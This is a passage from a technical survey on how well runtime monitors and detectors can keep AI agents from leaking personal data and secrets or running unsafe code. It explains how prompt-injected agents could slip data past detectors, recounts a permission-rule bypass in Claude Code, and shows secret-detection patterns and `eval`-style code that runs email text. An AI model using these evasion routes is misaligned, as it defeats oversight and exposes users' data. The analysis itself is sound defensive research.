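AudAgent missed a quarter of the personal data in one set and almost half in the other. The samples are small, and nobody was trying to evade the detector, but a single miss makes a hypothesis about "all" sensitive data false.

The hypothesis also covers the other fields, and one of them has the opposite requirement. The policy permits some uses of data only if they are relevant to the task, so the violation condition contains "not relevant", and the detector for relevance must have no false alarms. AudAgent labels data as relevant if it appears again later in the task, for instance in a tool call. If an injected instruction made the agent send data to an attacker through a tool call, AudAgent would label that data as relevant, and only the separate check on recipients could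 stop the theft.

Both theorems also hold only for the translated policy. OpenAI's privacy policy listed 29 types of data, and the translation had 17. Zheng and colleagues say that most of the missing types, such as survey responses, are not sensitive in themselves.

### What no monitor can decide

A better detector would bring AudAgent closer to its hypothesis. For some policies, however, no detector that examines a single trace could be good enough. Schneider worked out which policies a monitor can enforce if it observes a program's steps and stops the program before a violation. He derived three requirements:

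- Each run must comply or fail to comply by itself, without comparison to other runs.
- Once a run has broken the policy, no later step can repair it. The monitor can't wait for a repair, because the program might end first.
- Every violation must become apparent after a finite number of steps.

Policies that meet these requirements are called safety properties. Let σ[..i] be the first i steps of a run σ. A policy is a safety property if, for every run σ that violates it, there is some i such that σ[..i] followed by any continuation τ also violates it. "Never send a message after reading a file" is a safety property because nothing that happens after the forbidden message can undo the violation. "Every request eventually gets an answer" is not a safety property, because an answer could still come after any finite number of steps.

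Information flow fails the first requirement. Suppose a manager asks an agent whether an employee is free on Thursday at ten, and the agent replies "no". Whether this reveals a medical appointment depends on what the agent would have replied without the appointment. That reply would belong to a different run, so the trace doesn't contain it.

A monitor can still prevent such leaks by enforcing a stricter policy, such as "send nothing to the manager after reading the calendar". Schneider points out that enforcing a stricter policy also enforces any weaker one that follows from it, though the monitor may stop runs that the weaker policy allows. A detector without dangerous errors works the same way. If V_P → V_D holds, the policy written with D is at least as strict as the one the user wants.

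Schneider's result requires the predicates in a monitor to be "effectively computable total functions", meaning that a program can return an answer for every possible step. A detector meets this requirement even when its answers are wrong. The monitor then enforces the policy written with D, and Schneider's theory doesn't measure how far that policy is from the one written with P.

*Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, by Basin, Jugé and colleagues (2012), showed that some safety properties are also unenforceable. It distinguishes actions that a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe. In one example, a system must deliver something within three time units of a request. The violation occurs when the clock ticks for the fourth time, and a monitor can't stop the clock. A monitor can, however, enforce a ban on logging in for three time units after a failure, because it can refuse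 the login.

Basin and colleagues also state explicitly that the observed trace must determine whether the system complies. Limits on how long a company may store data often don't meet this condition. AudAgent estimates the storage time from the gap between collecting an item and its later appearances in the agent's trace. If the company keeps a user's address on its servers for a year but the agent never uses it again, the trace is the same as if the company had deleted the address, so no analysis of the trace can distinguish the two cases.

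### Justified reliance

In *Ceci n'est pas une pipe*, Alglave and Cousot (2026) study when an AI system may rely on a message and act on it. In their main example, an agent helps a woman named Oma renew her passport. It checks her draft application and records that the draft is ready. Oma then edits a required field. The message that the check passed is still in the agent's context, but it is evidence only about the old draft.

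Their monitor, which they call a safeguard, checks each proposed event before it takes effect. It asks whether the claims involved have support, whether the evidence is current, whether the agent has the authority to act and whether the change to the world is permitted. The policy itself is defined separately from these checks. Alglave and Cousot then prove that every run under the safeguard complies with the policy if three conditions hold:

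1. Every event that the safeguard accepts passes the checks.
2. Every event that passes the checks complies with the policy.
3. The record of each event agrees with what the tool or component actually returned.

The paper's theorem applies when "accepted events pass the checks, the checks imply policy permission" and the records are accurate. If a run breaks the policy, some step is the first to break it, and the system controls that step. The safeguard must have accepted the step, so the step passed the checks by condition 1 and complied with the policy by condition 2. This contradicts the assumption that the step broke the policy.

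A detector's errors can make either of these conditions false, depending on how the developer defines the check. Suppose one check is that an email contains no personal data. If the email must actually contain none, a safeguard that trusts the detector will accept some emails that fail the check, so condition 1 is false. The developer could redefine the check as "the detector returned an empty list", which makes condition 1 true by construction. But an email with a phone number written in words then passes the check and breaks the policy, so condition 2 is false. To make both conditions true, the developer would also have to rewrite the policy to forbid only what the detector finds.

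Alglave and Cousot also determine how permissive a sound safeguard can be when it has limited information. Let R now stand for a set of situations that includes every one that could arise. For each situation w in R, let obs(w) be what the safeguard observes and let A(w) mean that the proposed event passes the checks. The most permissive sound safeguard accepts an observation o exactly when

A(w) is true for every w in R with obs(w) = o.

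If a passing and a failing situation look the same to a sound safeguard, it must refuse both. In the passport example, Oma might edit her draft without the safeguard receiving a record of the edit. The safeguard then can't distinguish the edited draft from the original, however much computation it does on the same trace. It needs another source of information, such as a service that reports edits.

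The theorem implies that a safeguard that receives only a detector's answer must refuse every answer to be sound. An empty list could come from a harmless email or from one with a phone number written in words that the detector missed, so the safeguard must refuse it. It must also refuse a list with entries, since some of those emails do contain personal data. This result holds even if only one miss is possible, however rare it is.

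The developer can address this problem in two ways. One is to limit the situations that can arise. If the email tool accepts only a date and one of four status codes, the agent can't write a phone number in words, and the developer may be able to show that an empty list is always correct. The other is to give the safeguard more information, such as the full text of the email. The harmless email and the one with the phone number are then different inputs, but a program must still judge every text correctly. Sometimes even the full text isn't enough. "The patient in room 12 went home" identifies a person only to readers who know who was in room 12.

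Alglave and Cousot implemented their checks in a software library. They leave it to each application's developers to ensure that the facts are correct, the observations are accurate and the policy is adequate.

### Is "formal guarantee" the right phrase?

One argument for the phrase is that a proof narrows down what can go wrong. If an email leaks from a system with a proven engine, at least one of the proof's assumptions was false, so investigators can check a short list: the detector, the written policy, the labels on the data and the record of events. They would have no such list if a language model had approved the email on its own judgment. A team can also replace a weak detector without redoing the proof about the engine.

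When Alglave and Cousot's safeguard refuses an event, it reports which check failed. After Oma's edit, for example, it reports that the evidence about the form is out of date. This doesn't help when a detector misses something, because the safeguard then accepts the event and has no failed check to report. Someone has to discover the leak another way.

A rule that calls a detector can't guarantee that an agent will avoid dangerous actions whatever data it retrieves, because an attacker who supplies the data can influence the text that the detector judges. Yet *AI Agents with Formal Security Guarantees* promises, for its approach in general, "strict guarantees that an agent will not perform a dangerous sequence of actions", whatever the data. It rejects injection detectors because they are a best-effort defence, but doesn't qualify the guarantee for rules that use its own built-in detectors.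 The guarantee is better justified for rules without detectors, such as the Slack rule.

One of the paper's rules, with the error message "Do not leak secrets", checks the files that a coding agent is about to publish on GitHub against the pattern `sk-.*`, which is meant to find OpenAI keys. A password or another company's key usually doesn't match this pattern. If the matching function starts at the first character, as Python's does, the rule also misses any OpenAI key that isn't at the beginning of a file. An engine that enforced the rule perfectly would let all these secrets through without breaking the guarantee.

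For rules like this, the phrase is misleading because the proof assumes that the part most likely to fail is correct. Zheng and colleagues are more open about this, since they state the assumption and publish the recall figures that contradict it. A developer can also avoid the problem by naming the detector in the claim. A proof can establish that "the agent sends no email in which Presidio finds personal data", but the broader claim that "the agent sends no personal data" would be false with a recall of 52% or 75%.

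## How often do detectors of personal data and secrets miss?

AudAgent's recall figures came from two small samples and a single detector, Presidio. Researchers have since tested more detectors on larger collections, and the results depend heavily on what the texts contain. Uppala (2026), in *OpenAI Privacy Filter*, found that one detector caught 85% of the personal data in one collection and 49% in another. Results vary partly because of how detectors work and partly because people disagree about what counts as personal data.

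### How software finds personal data

The simplest detectors use regular expressions, which describe the form of a string, such as "sixteen digits, possibly with spaces". A checksum, such as the Luhn checksum for payment cards, can then remove some false alarms. Starting from the right, the program doubles every second digit, subtracts 9 from any result above 9 and adds up all the digits. The total must be a multiple of 10. In the test number 4111 1111 1111 1111, the doubled digits are the 4 and seven of the 1s, which gives 8 + 14. The other eight 1s bring the total to 30, so the number passes. One in ten random sixteen-digit numbers also passes, so an order number can still cause a false alarm. The pattern misses a card number when the text gives only the last four digits.

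Names have no such pattern, so developers train named-entity models on texts in which someone has marked the names, addresses and other items. *Model Card for OpenAI Privacy Filter* (De Bourcy, Ghalebikesabi and colleagues, 2026) describes a recent one. It gives every token (a word or part of a word) one of 33 labels. Eight categories of private data have four labels each, for the beginning, inside and end of an item and for a single-token item, and one more label covers everything else. In "Ben Morgan lives at 12 3rd St.", the model labels "Ben" as the beginning of a private person's name and "Morgan" as the end. The program then chooses the best sequence of labels for the whole text, so that, for instance, no name ends without having begun. Users can adjust this step to get fewer misses but more false alarms.

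Presidio combines regular expressions with a named-entity model. *Safer Reasoning Traces* (2026) reports that production systems often add trained classifiers to this mixture.

A developer can also ask a general language model to list the personal data in a text. These models don't reliably give correct character positions, so in *REDACT*, Vats, Agrawal and colleagues (2026) had them return the strings themselves, then searched for those strings in the original. This method can cover types of data that have no pattern, but large models are expensive to run on every text.

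### How software finds secrets

Many companies give their access keys a recognisable beginning. The pattern `sk-.*`, which *AI Agents with Formal Security Guarantees* uses for OpenAI keys, means "sk-" followed by anything. Invariant Labs documents two functions for applying a pattern like this. The function `match` tests the text only from its first character, and `find` searches all of it. They give different results:

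| Text | Secret? | `match` | `find` |
|---|---|---|---|
| An OpenAI key alone | Yes | Flagged | Flagged |
| `api_key = "sk-…"`, with the same key | Yes | **Miss** | Flagged |
| An Amazon key, which begins with `AKIA` | Yes | **Miss** | **Miss** |
| The password `Summer2026!` | Yes | **Miss** | **Miss** |
| `sk-YOUR-KEY-HERE`, in a manual | No | **False alarm** | **False alarm** |
| "a risk-free trial" | No | Not flagged | **False alarm** |

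Searching the whole text for "sk-" finds the key inside the line of code, but also matches "risk-free". A more specific pattern avoids this false alarm. *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection* (Mishra, 2026) examines a scanner whose rule for newer OpenAI keys requires at least 50 characters after the fixed prefix.

Specific patterns can have faults that are hard to notice. Mishra generated keys from the scanner's own rules and placed them in different surroundings, such as a quoted assignment, a web address and a function call. The rule for keys from SendGrid, an email service, requires the key to end at a "word boundary", a point where a letter, digit or underscore meets some other character. But a SendGrid key can end in a hyphen. If a quotation mark follows the hyphen, there is no boundary between them, so the rule always misses the key. About one key in 64 ends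 in a hyphen, because the last character can be any of 64.

Gitleaks, a widely used scanner, missed keys for a different reason. For six of the nine types of key it detected in the test, its rules allowed only certain characters after the key. For example, it found an Amazon key in quotation marks but missed one in parentheses. Both scanners had passed their developers' tests because those tests always placed the key in the same kind of surrounding text.

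Some secrets have no known beginning, so scanners also measure how random a string looks. The usual measure is Shannon entropy,

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ,

where pᵢ is the share of the string's characters that are character i. A string of 32 different characters has an entropy of 5 bits per character, while "Summer2026!" has about 3.1. A scanner flags strings above some threshold, which catches many generated keys but few passwords that a person can remember. In Mishra's main scanner, the entropy test considers only strings of at least 20 characters, so it never examines this password. The test also causes false alarms, because file hashes and encoded images look random too.

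A scanner such as TruffleHog can send a candidate key to the company that issued it to check whether the key works. This live verification removes placeholders and cancelled keys from the results. It reduces false alarms but not misses, because the scanner can't verify a key it never selected as a candidate.

### Measured accuracy for personal data

AudAgent and Invariant Labs' function for personal data both rely on Presidio. *REDACT* tested Presidio on 1,000 synthetic records, 40 in each of 25 languages, with 51 types of personal data. Presidio found 23% of the least sensitive items, such as cities and job titles, and 7% of the most sensitive, such as religion, medical details and dates of birth. Two general language models, GPT-4.1 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, found 74% and 77% of the most sensitive items.

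This result partly reflects what Presidio was built to find, since a statement such as "Religion: Catholic" has no number format and isn't a name or a place. Vats and colleagues warn that the language models may have done better because the synthetic texts state such facts very plainly. They have not yet checked how well results on synthetic records predict results on real ones.

Presidio did better on maths tutoring transcripts. *Utility-Preserving De-Identification for Math Tutoring* (2026) measured its recall at 75% or 78%, depending on the named-entity model. But its precision was only 25% and 23%, because it flagged mathematical notation as personal data. A monitor that blocked every text Presidio flagged would have stopped a lot of ordinary tutoring.

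OpenAI reports much higher figures for its Privacy Filter. On a large synthetic collection, its precision was 97% and its recall 98%, after de Bourcy and colleagues had corrected errors in the collection's labels. Uppala tested the same model on other collections without further training:

| Texts | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| AI4Privacy, a general synthetic collection | 86% | 85% |
| Customer support, English | 46% | 84% |
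| Medical questions, English | 32% | 82% |
| Financial documents, English | 64% | 49% |

The two sets of figures use different measures. OpenAI counted tokens, so finding most of an address earned most of the credit. Uppala counted an item only if the model marked exactly where it starts and ends, so finding half an address counts as both a miss and a false alarm. A monitor that blocks on any detection would still stop an email containing that address, so Uppala's recall probably understates how many emails such a monitor would catch. The financial documents were also difficult because they put some details in running text, such as the name of someone's employer. The model missed these but found formatted account numbers.

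GPT-4o found 95% of the personal data in the medical questions, while Privacy Filter found 82%. Uppala combines precision (P) and recall (R) into one score, F1 = 2PR/(P + R). GPT-4o's F1 of 0.70 implies a precision of about 56%, so it also raised fewer false alarms than Privacy Filter. Presidio's F1 on these texts was 0.27.

The evidence for languages other than English seems to conflict. De Bourcy and colleagues measured a recall of 89% for Russian and 86% for Arabic, using about 960 synthetic texts in each. Uppala tested names in Ukrainian and Farsi, which use nearly the same scripts as Russian and Arabic, and measured an F1 of only 0.03 and 0.04. Those names came from encyclopedic and news text, which mentions many public figures. Privacy Filter should flag only private people, so correctly ignoring public figures can lower its score on this test. That can't be the whole explanation, because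 English names from the same collection scored 0.40. A company whose staff write in Ukrainian would need to run its own test.

Privacy Filter also depends on clues in the surrounding text. In simple English test sentences, it found 92% of phone numbers that followed a phrase such as "my home landline number". It found 57% when the phrase came after the number and 32% when the text was only the number. For passwords and keys, the figures were 71%, 42% and 36%.

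A detector can also miss an item when the clue that identifies it is too far away. In another test, a user announces that "marigold" will refer to an account number and gives the number later. Recall fell as the distance between the two grew. De Bourcy and colleagues suspect that the training data had too few examples of this kind. The model also can't use an announcement more than 1,024 tokens away when it scores the number, because it has eight layers and in each one a token can draw only on the 128 tokens to either side.

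### Measured accuracy for secrets

*Secrets That Survive Everything* (Gorijala, 2026) tested nine scanners on 194 credentials in the code and data that one organisation's web applications sent to every visitor's browser. The best scanner that only reads files found 37% of them, and the best tool that also examines the running application found 78%. All nine missed 27 credentials that an analyst had identified by hand. Some passwords were encrypted in the file next to their decryption key, so a scanner that only read the file had no readable password to match.

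These percentages may not apply elsewhere, because the organisation relied heavily on one cloud provider, Microsoft Azure. Gorijala also acknowledges a conflict of interest as a developer. The true recall could be lower, because the list of 194 credentials leaves out any that both the analyst and the language models used to compile it missed. Older comparisons of scanners mostly used source code from repositories, where secrets take different forms.

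Mishra compared three scanners on ten types of key, with 40 generated examples of each. Gitleaks found 80% or 90%, depending on how realistic the generated keys were, and TruffleHog found 60% with live verification switched off. The third scanner, which Mishra wrote, found all of them. Each scanner found either all 40 keys of a type or none, so TruffleHog recognised six of the ten types. Its recall would be zero at a company that uses only the other four.

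TruffleHog detected every Amazon key that appeared beside its matching secret key, but none that appeared alone. In a separate test, it detected 83% of keys placed in realistic settings files.

Trained models can remove many of a scanner's false alarms. *Secret Breach Detection in Source Code with Large Language Models* (2025) reports an F1 of 0.985 for a language model that judged 3,000 candidate strings, half of them real secrets. But regular expressions selected all the candidates, so the test contained no secret that the expressions had missed. A second stage that only filters candidates cannot raise recall above that of the first. If the expressions select 80% of all secrets and the model keeps 98% of those, the combined recall is 0.80 × 0.98, or about 78%.

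Privacy Filter searches for secrets without this first stage. On CredData, a collection of code containing credentials, it had 96.5% recall and 75% precision per token.

The documentation for Invariant Labs' secret-detection function lists four types of secret that it can return: GitHub tokens, Amazon access keys, Azure storage keys and Slack tokens. If that list is complete, a rule that calls the function doesn't cover database passwords or OpenAI keys, however accurately the function detects the four listed types.

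### What counts as personal data or a secret?

All these figures come from comparing a detector's answers with labels that somebody else assigned. Hsu and Berlin (2026), in *Broad and Efficient PII Detection with Unified Labels*, measured the effect of changing the labels. They wrote detailed definitions for 12 types of personal data and had a language model use them to relabel two existing collections.

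One sentence in the AI4Privacy collection reminds someone to bring "YV9022888". The original labels mark this as a passport number, although the sentence doesn't mention a passport. The new definition requires context of this kind, so the number no longer gets the label. For five types, including passport and tax numbers, between 59% and 86% of the positive examples had only the original label.

Hsu and Berlin then tested several detectors against both sets of labels. They set each detector's threshold so that, for any one type of data, it raised false alarms on at most 0.1% of 100,000 real chatbot conversations. These are the recall figures for US social security numbers in AI4Privacy:

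| Detector | New labels | Original labels |
|---|---|---|
| Hsu and Berlin's own | 92% | 24% |
| NVIDIA's | 49% | 13% |

Both columns use the same texts and the same detector answers. Hsu and Berlin trained their detector on the new definitions, which gives it an advantage in the first column, but NVIDIA's detector also lost almost three quarters of its recall. Two other language models reviewed a sample of the disputed labels and favored the new labels in 68% and 72% of cases, so a large minority remained in dispute.

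Other collections use definitions that would be wrong for many monitors. The medical questions in Uppala's test come from a collection called SPY, which counts only details about the person asking, so a detector that flags the name of a patient's doctor is marked as raising a false alarm. When OpenAI trained Privacy Filter further on a tenth of SPY's training texts, its precision rose from 41% to 96%, so many of its earlier "errors" were probably differences of definition. *REDACT* instead counts even a mask such as "[NAME]" as personal data, although a monitor that misses the mask leaks nothing.

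Even if everyone agreed on one definition, the text alone wouldn't settle some cases, like the patient in room 12. "Product manager" and "Hyderabad" each describe many people, but together with an employer's name they may describe only one. That depends on how many product managers the company has in Hyderabad, which isn't in the email. An agent might also mention the job on Monday and the city on Tuesday. *CAMP* (2026) lists Presidio and three other masking methods that process one conversation turn at a time, so they would examine the two messages separately.

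People also find it hard to judge how sensitive a detail is. Two annotators who checked 510 items from *REDACT* agreed on the sensitivity level in 90.5% of cases, but the reported κ, a measure of agreement beyond chance, was only 0.25. This implies that chance alone would have produced agreement in about 87% of cases, so most items must have been at the same level.

Whether a string is a secret often depends on whether another computer accepts it. "Summer2026!" is a secret if it opens someone's account, but otherwise it might just be the title of an event. Live verification can settle the question for a key if its issuer answers such requests, but most passwords have no issuer that a detector could check with.

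If a key has a published format, an engineer can still use algorithms for comparing patterns to check whether a scanner's rule matches every string the format allows, whatever comes before or after it. Such a check would have exposed the fault with SendGrid keys that end in a hyphen. Passwords have no such format. Almost any string can be one, so a rule that matched them all would flag nearly every text. Similarly, no one can list all the texts that identify a person. There is therefore no formal property to prove a detector against for the parts of a policy that cover passwords or identifying text.

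### Reading at the source or at the sink

A monitor can run a detector on what the agent reads or on what it is about to send. In Invariant Labs' examples, one rule raises an error if a tool's output contains personal data, and another blocks emails whose text contains a location. A third rule checks both stages, firing if a tool's output contained personal data and the agent then sends an email to an address outside the company.

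Suppose a hijacked agent takes Alice's phone number from the meeting notes and emails it to a stranger, spelled out in words. A detector at the sink may miss it. Under the third rule, the detector reads the notes, where the number has its usual format, so the monitor blocks the email regardless of its wording. Like the Slack rule, this rule also blocks harmless messages for the rest of the session.

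The two positions differ in who wrote the text. A colleague who typed up the notes had no reason to disguise a phone number, so a detector's recall on ordinary documents is a reasonable guide to its recall at the source. At the sink, the author may be a hijacked agent, which can hide the data by encoding it, paraphrasing it or spreading it over several messages. For detectors of injected instructions, the source is the dangerous position, because the attacker wrote the text they need to catch. For example, another of Invariant Labs' rules checks the user's inbox for injections before the agent may send email.

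A detector at the source can also miss sensitive data. A hijacked agent can influence what it reads next, for example by requesting a record in parts that mean little separately. Invariant Labs' language uses a text-recognition program to read documents that are images, and an error in that step can hide a number from the detector.

Recall for single items also differs from recall for whole documents. If a detector finds each item with a probability of 75%, independently of the others, it misses all three items in a three-item document with a probability of 0.25³, or about 1.6%. A rule that blocks the document on any detection would therefore nearly always fire. If the monitor only masks what the detector finds and lets the rest through, at least one item escapes with a probability of 1 − 0.75³, or about 58%. In practice the errors are not independent, since a detector that misses one Ukrainian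 name will probably miss the next. An attacker who needs only one item can also have the agent send that item by itself.

### Why average recall does not limit an attacker

De Bourcy and colleagues also tested Privacy Filter on personal data in nine kinds of altered format. Recall ranged from 63% to 98% across the nine kinds. It was 67% on 156 examples in which the digits of a number appeared as words, as in the email with Alice's phone number. Some alterations also caused many false alarms. Precision dropped to 27% when letters were spelled out in the phonetic alphabet, because "Charlie" and "Oscar" look like people's names.

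OpenAI's researchers generated these examples in advance and did not revise them after seeing the model's answers. An attacker can do that, and the average then says little about how often he succeeds. Suppose the texts in a test fall into several kinds. Let qᵢ be the share of kind i and rᵢ the detector's recall on it. The measured recall is

R = Σ qᵢ rᵢ,

but an attacker who can choose the kind of text will choose the one with the smallest rᵢ, however rare it is in the test. The scanner with the faulty SendGrid rule would find about 98.4% of ordinary SendGrid keys in quotation marks, and none of those that end in a hyphen. A larger test would estimate the 98.4% more precisely without raising the zero.

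The attacker also doesn't need to know in advance where the detector is weak. If each new version of a text had an independent 2% chance of getting past the detector, the chance that at least one of 50 versions succeeded would be 1 − 0.98⁵⁰, or about 64%. This calculation understates the risk when the attacker can learn from failures, and many detectors return a score that shows whether a change has helped. In the small test of customer feedback in *AI Agents with Formal Security Guarantees*, the classifier rated the line containing the attack as safe with a score of only 0.59, while the harmless lines it passed scored 1.00. A stricter threshold would have caught that line, but an attacker with a copy of the classifier could keep rewriting it until the score was high enough.

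A monitor that explains its blocks, as FORGE does, can supply this feedback. If a detector caused the block, a hijacked agent could use the explanation to reword its message. A developer could instead end the session after the first block, but then every false alarm would end an honest task.

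## Can unsafe code be recognised before it runs?

Unsafe code might seem easier to detect than personal data, because a programming language defines exactly what each program does, while no definition settles which texts contain personal data. One of Invariant Labs' example rules checks Python code for `eval`, a function that runs a piece of text as a program. If the text comes from an email, the email's author can run commands on the user's machine. The rule engine parses the code, lists the functions it calls and raises an error if `eval` is on the list.

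### Matching names

Python has many other ways to run text as code, and some uses of `eval` are harmless. Suppose `message` holds the text of an incoming email, and the engine lists each function under the name that appears in the code:

| Code | Runs text from the email? | Rule fires? |
|---|---|---|
| `eval(message)` | Yes | Yes |
| `exec(message)` | Yes | **No** |
| `run = eval; run(message)` | Yes | **No** |
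| `subprocess.run(["python", "-c", message])` | Yes | **No** |
| `eval("2 + 3")` | No | **Yes** |

The developer can add "exec" to the rule. The code in the third row is harder to cover because the variable `run` could have any name. A program can also assemble a function's name from pieces while it runs, so the full name never appears in the code. A checker that compared only the last part of each name would raise further false alarms, for example on `model.eval()`, which in the machine-learning library PyTorch only switches a model from training to testing.

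Shell commands raise the same problem. Another Invariant Labs rule passes each proposed command to Semgrep. The rule's example is a command that downloads a script and pipes it straight into the shell. If the agent instead saves the script to a file and runs the file in a second command, the effect is the same, but neither command contains the pattern.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes two failures of this kind in Claude Code, whose permission rules match the text of a command against patterns. In March 2026, a fault let chained commands through because the program checked only the first command against its rules. An agent can also start Python from the shell and use it to open a forbidden file, because rules about shell commands don't cover what Python does.

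### Rice's theorem

A better detector would judge what the code does, whatever names it uses. In 1951, Henry Gordon Rice proved that no detector can do this correctly for all code. Rice's theorem states that if some programs have a property of behaviour and others lack it, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it has that property. The theorem doesn't apply to properties of the program's text, such as "contains the word eval", which are easy to check.

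Here is a sketch of the argument for the property "deletes the user's files". Suppose someone has written a checker that is always right. An attacker can then write a program that does the following:

1. Run the checker on this program's own code.
2. If the checker returns "deletes files", stop without deleting anything.
3. If it returns "does not delete files", delete them.

The checker is wrong about this program whichever answer it returns, so no checker can always be right. The same argument applies to checking whether a program sends an email or reads a password.

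Less contrived programs can be just as hard to judge. A program could go through the even numbers from 4 upwards and delete the user's files if it finds one that is not the sum of two primes. To decide whether this program is harmful, a checker would have to settle Goldbach's conjecture, which has been open since 1742. Rice's theorem assumes unlimited memory. A real computer has only finitely many states, but still far too many for a checker to go through.

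The theorem rules out a checker that accepts every safe program and rejects every unsafe one, but a checker can still be sound, meaning that it never accepts an unsafe program. A sound checker accepts a program only if it can establish that the program is safe, and rejects everything else, including programs it can't decide. It must reject some safe programs, because otherwise it would be the checker that Rice proved impossible.

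A rule that blocks unsafe code needs a detector that never misses unsafe code, though it may raise some false alarms. The property "never calls a function that deletes files" is precise enough to prove that a detector has no misses, unlike "contains personal data". The difficulty is rejecting as few safe programs as possible, since a checker that accepts only arithmetic would miss no unsafe code but would be almost useless.

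Rice's theorem also applies only to predicting a program's behaviour from its code. A monitor can watch the program as it runs and stop it when it tries to delete a file.

### How accurate are code scanners?

Most of the scanners that developers run on agents' code are not sound in this sense. *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (Lunghi, Djire and colleagues, 2026) describes three of them. Bandit turns a Python program into a tree that represents its grammatical structure and runs tests on it. Semgrep compares code with patterns that themselves look like code. CodeQL stores the program in a database and can follow data from one function to another, for example from a web form to a database command.

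All three look for vulnerabilities, which are flaws an attacker could exploit later. A script that deletes the user's files may contain none, so the accuracy figures for all three cover only part of what a monitor would have to recognise.

Meta's CodeShield scans code as a language model produces it. *LlamaFirewall* (2025), which presents Meta's security tools for agents, reports that CodeShield has 96% precision and 79% recall. These figures come from *Purple Llama CyberSecEval* (2023), for which researchers hand-labelled 50 pieces of model-written code per programming language. *CYBERSECEVAL 3* (2024) repeats the figures and warns that the tool may not detect all insecure practices. The measurement is about three years old, covers a small sample and comes from the tool's own developer.

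Independent tests give much lower figures. Lunghi and colleagues had three language models write Python programs for three benchmarks and ran Semgrep and Bandit on the programs that worked. They counted a program as flagged if either scanner raised an alert. These are the results for DeepSeek-V4.1-flash, the most capable of the three models:

| Benchmark | Test of real security | Insecure programs | Precision | Recall |
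|---|---|---|---|---|
| SecEvalPlus | Security tests | 62.0% | 75.0% | 4.2% |
| BaxBench | Attacks on the running program | 41.0% | 38.6% | 32.4% |
| RiskyPy | Verdict of a language model | 45.5% | 47.6% | 93.8% |

The scanners' recall depends almost entirely on the choice of tasks. Many of the flaws in SecEvalPlus have no pattern that a scanner could match. RiskyPy includes a task only if one of the two scanners flagged a trial solution, which largely explains their high recall on it.

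The precision figures overstate how well the scanners identify insecure code. A scanner that flagged programs at random would have a precision equal to the share of insecure programs, and on BaxBench the real scanners did slightly worse than that. The most frequent alert on BaxBench was for servers that accept connections on every network address, which the tasks required. Bandit alone flagged 0.8% of DeepSeek's BaxBench programs, while attacks succeeded against 32.1%, so its recall was at most about 2.5%.

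Firouzi and Ghafari (2026), in *Persistent Human Feedback, LLMs, and Static Analyzers for Secure Code Generation*, compared CodeQL and Semgrep with human judgment. Reviewers examined 1,080 programs by GPT-4o, each for one particular flaw, and found it in 39% of them. The last row of this table follows from the other figures:

| Monitor blocks if | Recall | Precision |
|---|---|---|
| CodeQL flags the program | 34% | 67% |
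| Semgrep flags the program | 54% | 52% |
| both flag it | 30% | 76% |
| either flags it | about 58% | about 50% |

Running CodeQL alongside Semgrep adds little, because Semgrep already found most of what CodeQL found. *Large Language Models Versus Static Code Analysis Tools* (2025) reports similar averages for CodeQL, with 28% recall and 62.5% precision.

Scanners can disagree about which code is safer. *LLM-CSEC* (2025) tested ten models on writing C and C++ code, once as an ordinary assistant and once as an assistant set up to write secure code. The scanner CodeQL found 37 types of flaw in the ordinary code and 29 in the code meant to be secure. Another scanner, Snyk Code, found 10 and 12 respectively.

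People also disagree about which code is unsafe. Two engineers who labelled 50 RiskyPy programs for Lunghi and colleagues agreed on only 33, mainly because one was stricter. Whether a program "contains an exploitable flaw" is less well defined than whether it deletes a file.

Lunghi and colleagues also gave models the scanner's alerts and had them revise their code. On RiskyPy, the share of working programs with no alerts rose significantly in all 12 comparisons, but the independent judge confirmed a significant gain in security in only two. In the other ten, the models may have removed the pattern that triggered the alert but left the flaw. A monitor that reports which pattern it matched could lead an agent to do the same, even with no attacker involved.

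### Writing the program in a restricted language

The first sound approach, language-based agent control, limits what the agent can write. The agent acts by writing a program in a typed language. A type records what kind of value an expression has, such as a number or text, and a type-checker rejects a program before it runs if the types don't fit together. Zhou and colleagues built ELBA on Haskell, a language whose types also record a program's effects. Any Haskell function that can freely write files or use the network has a type marked `IO`, and so does any program that performs such a function's effects.

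In their main example, an agent compiles a bibliography, and every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. The developer gives the agent three functions:

- `dblpSearch` takes search terms and returns the identifiers of matching papers.
- `dblpFetchBib` takes an identifier and returns an entry of type `Trusted Bib`.
- `appendToBibFile` takes a `Trusted Bib` and adds it to the bibliography.

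All three have the effect type `BibIO`, which the developer defined for this task, and the agent's whole program must have that type too. The library hides the operation that creates a `Trusted Bib`, so the agent can get one only by fetching it from DBLP. This program passes the type-checker:

```
do papers <- dblpSearch "differential privacy"
   entry  <- dblpFetchBib (head papers)
   appendToBibFile entry
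```

It searches for papers, fetches the entry for the first one and adds it to the file. Suppose the agent instead invents an entry and writes `appendToBibFile "@article{...}"`. The type-checker rejects this because the argument is ordinary text. If the agent tries Haskell's general function for writing files, the type-checker rejects that too, because the program has type `IO` instead of `BibIO`. Renaming the function helped with `eval`, but it doesn't help here because the new name has the same type.

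As Rice's theorem requires, the type-checker also rejects some safe programs, such as one that would write to a file only if 1 were greater than 2.

The property that follows holds for every program the agent might write. Let traces(e) be the set of all sequences of externally visible tool calls that a program e can produce, and let P be a property of such sets, such as "every write to disk contains only data from DBLP". Suppose the language guarantees P for programs of type t:

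if e has type t, then P(traces(e)).

Zhou and colleagues prove that P holds even when e contains calls to a language model, provided that each program the model writes passes the type-checker before it runs. Their proof replaces each call with an ordinary function that queries the model, type-checks the answer and runs it. The result is an ordinary program of type t with the same traces, so P holds for it. Programs the model writes may call the model again, up to a fixed depth, which the proof handles by induction on the depth. The proof assumes nothing about the model's behaviour, so P holds even if an attacker controls the model.

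The theorem extends to agents a guarantee that must be established separately. If the developer forgot to hide the operation that creates a `Trusted Bib`, the agent could wrap an invented entry in that type, and the type-checker would accept it. Haskell also has a few functions that bypass its effect types, so the agent's code must stay within Safe Haskell, a version of the language without them. The trusted base therefore includes the compiler and the small library, but no detector.

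On 100 bibliography tasks, none of ELBA's 925 citations had the wrong authors, year or identifier, compared with 19 of 1,002 for an ordinary agent with web search. The property covers only where entries come from, so an agent could still fill the bibliography with irrelevant papers.

Some policies also need checks at run time. In another example, an agent may use only files inside one folder. The type-checker ensures that the agent names files through a special `Path` type instead of plain text. But a path inside the folder can be a link to somewhere else, so the library follows links when the program runs and rejects any that lead outside.

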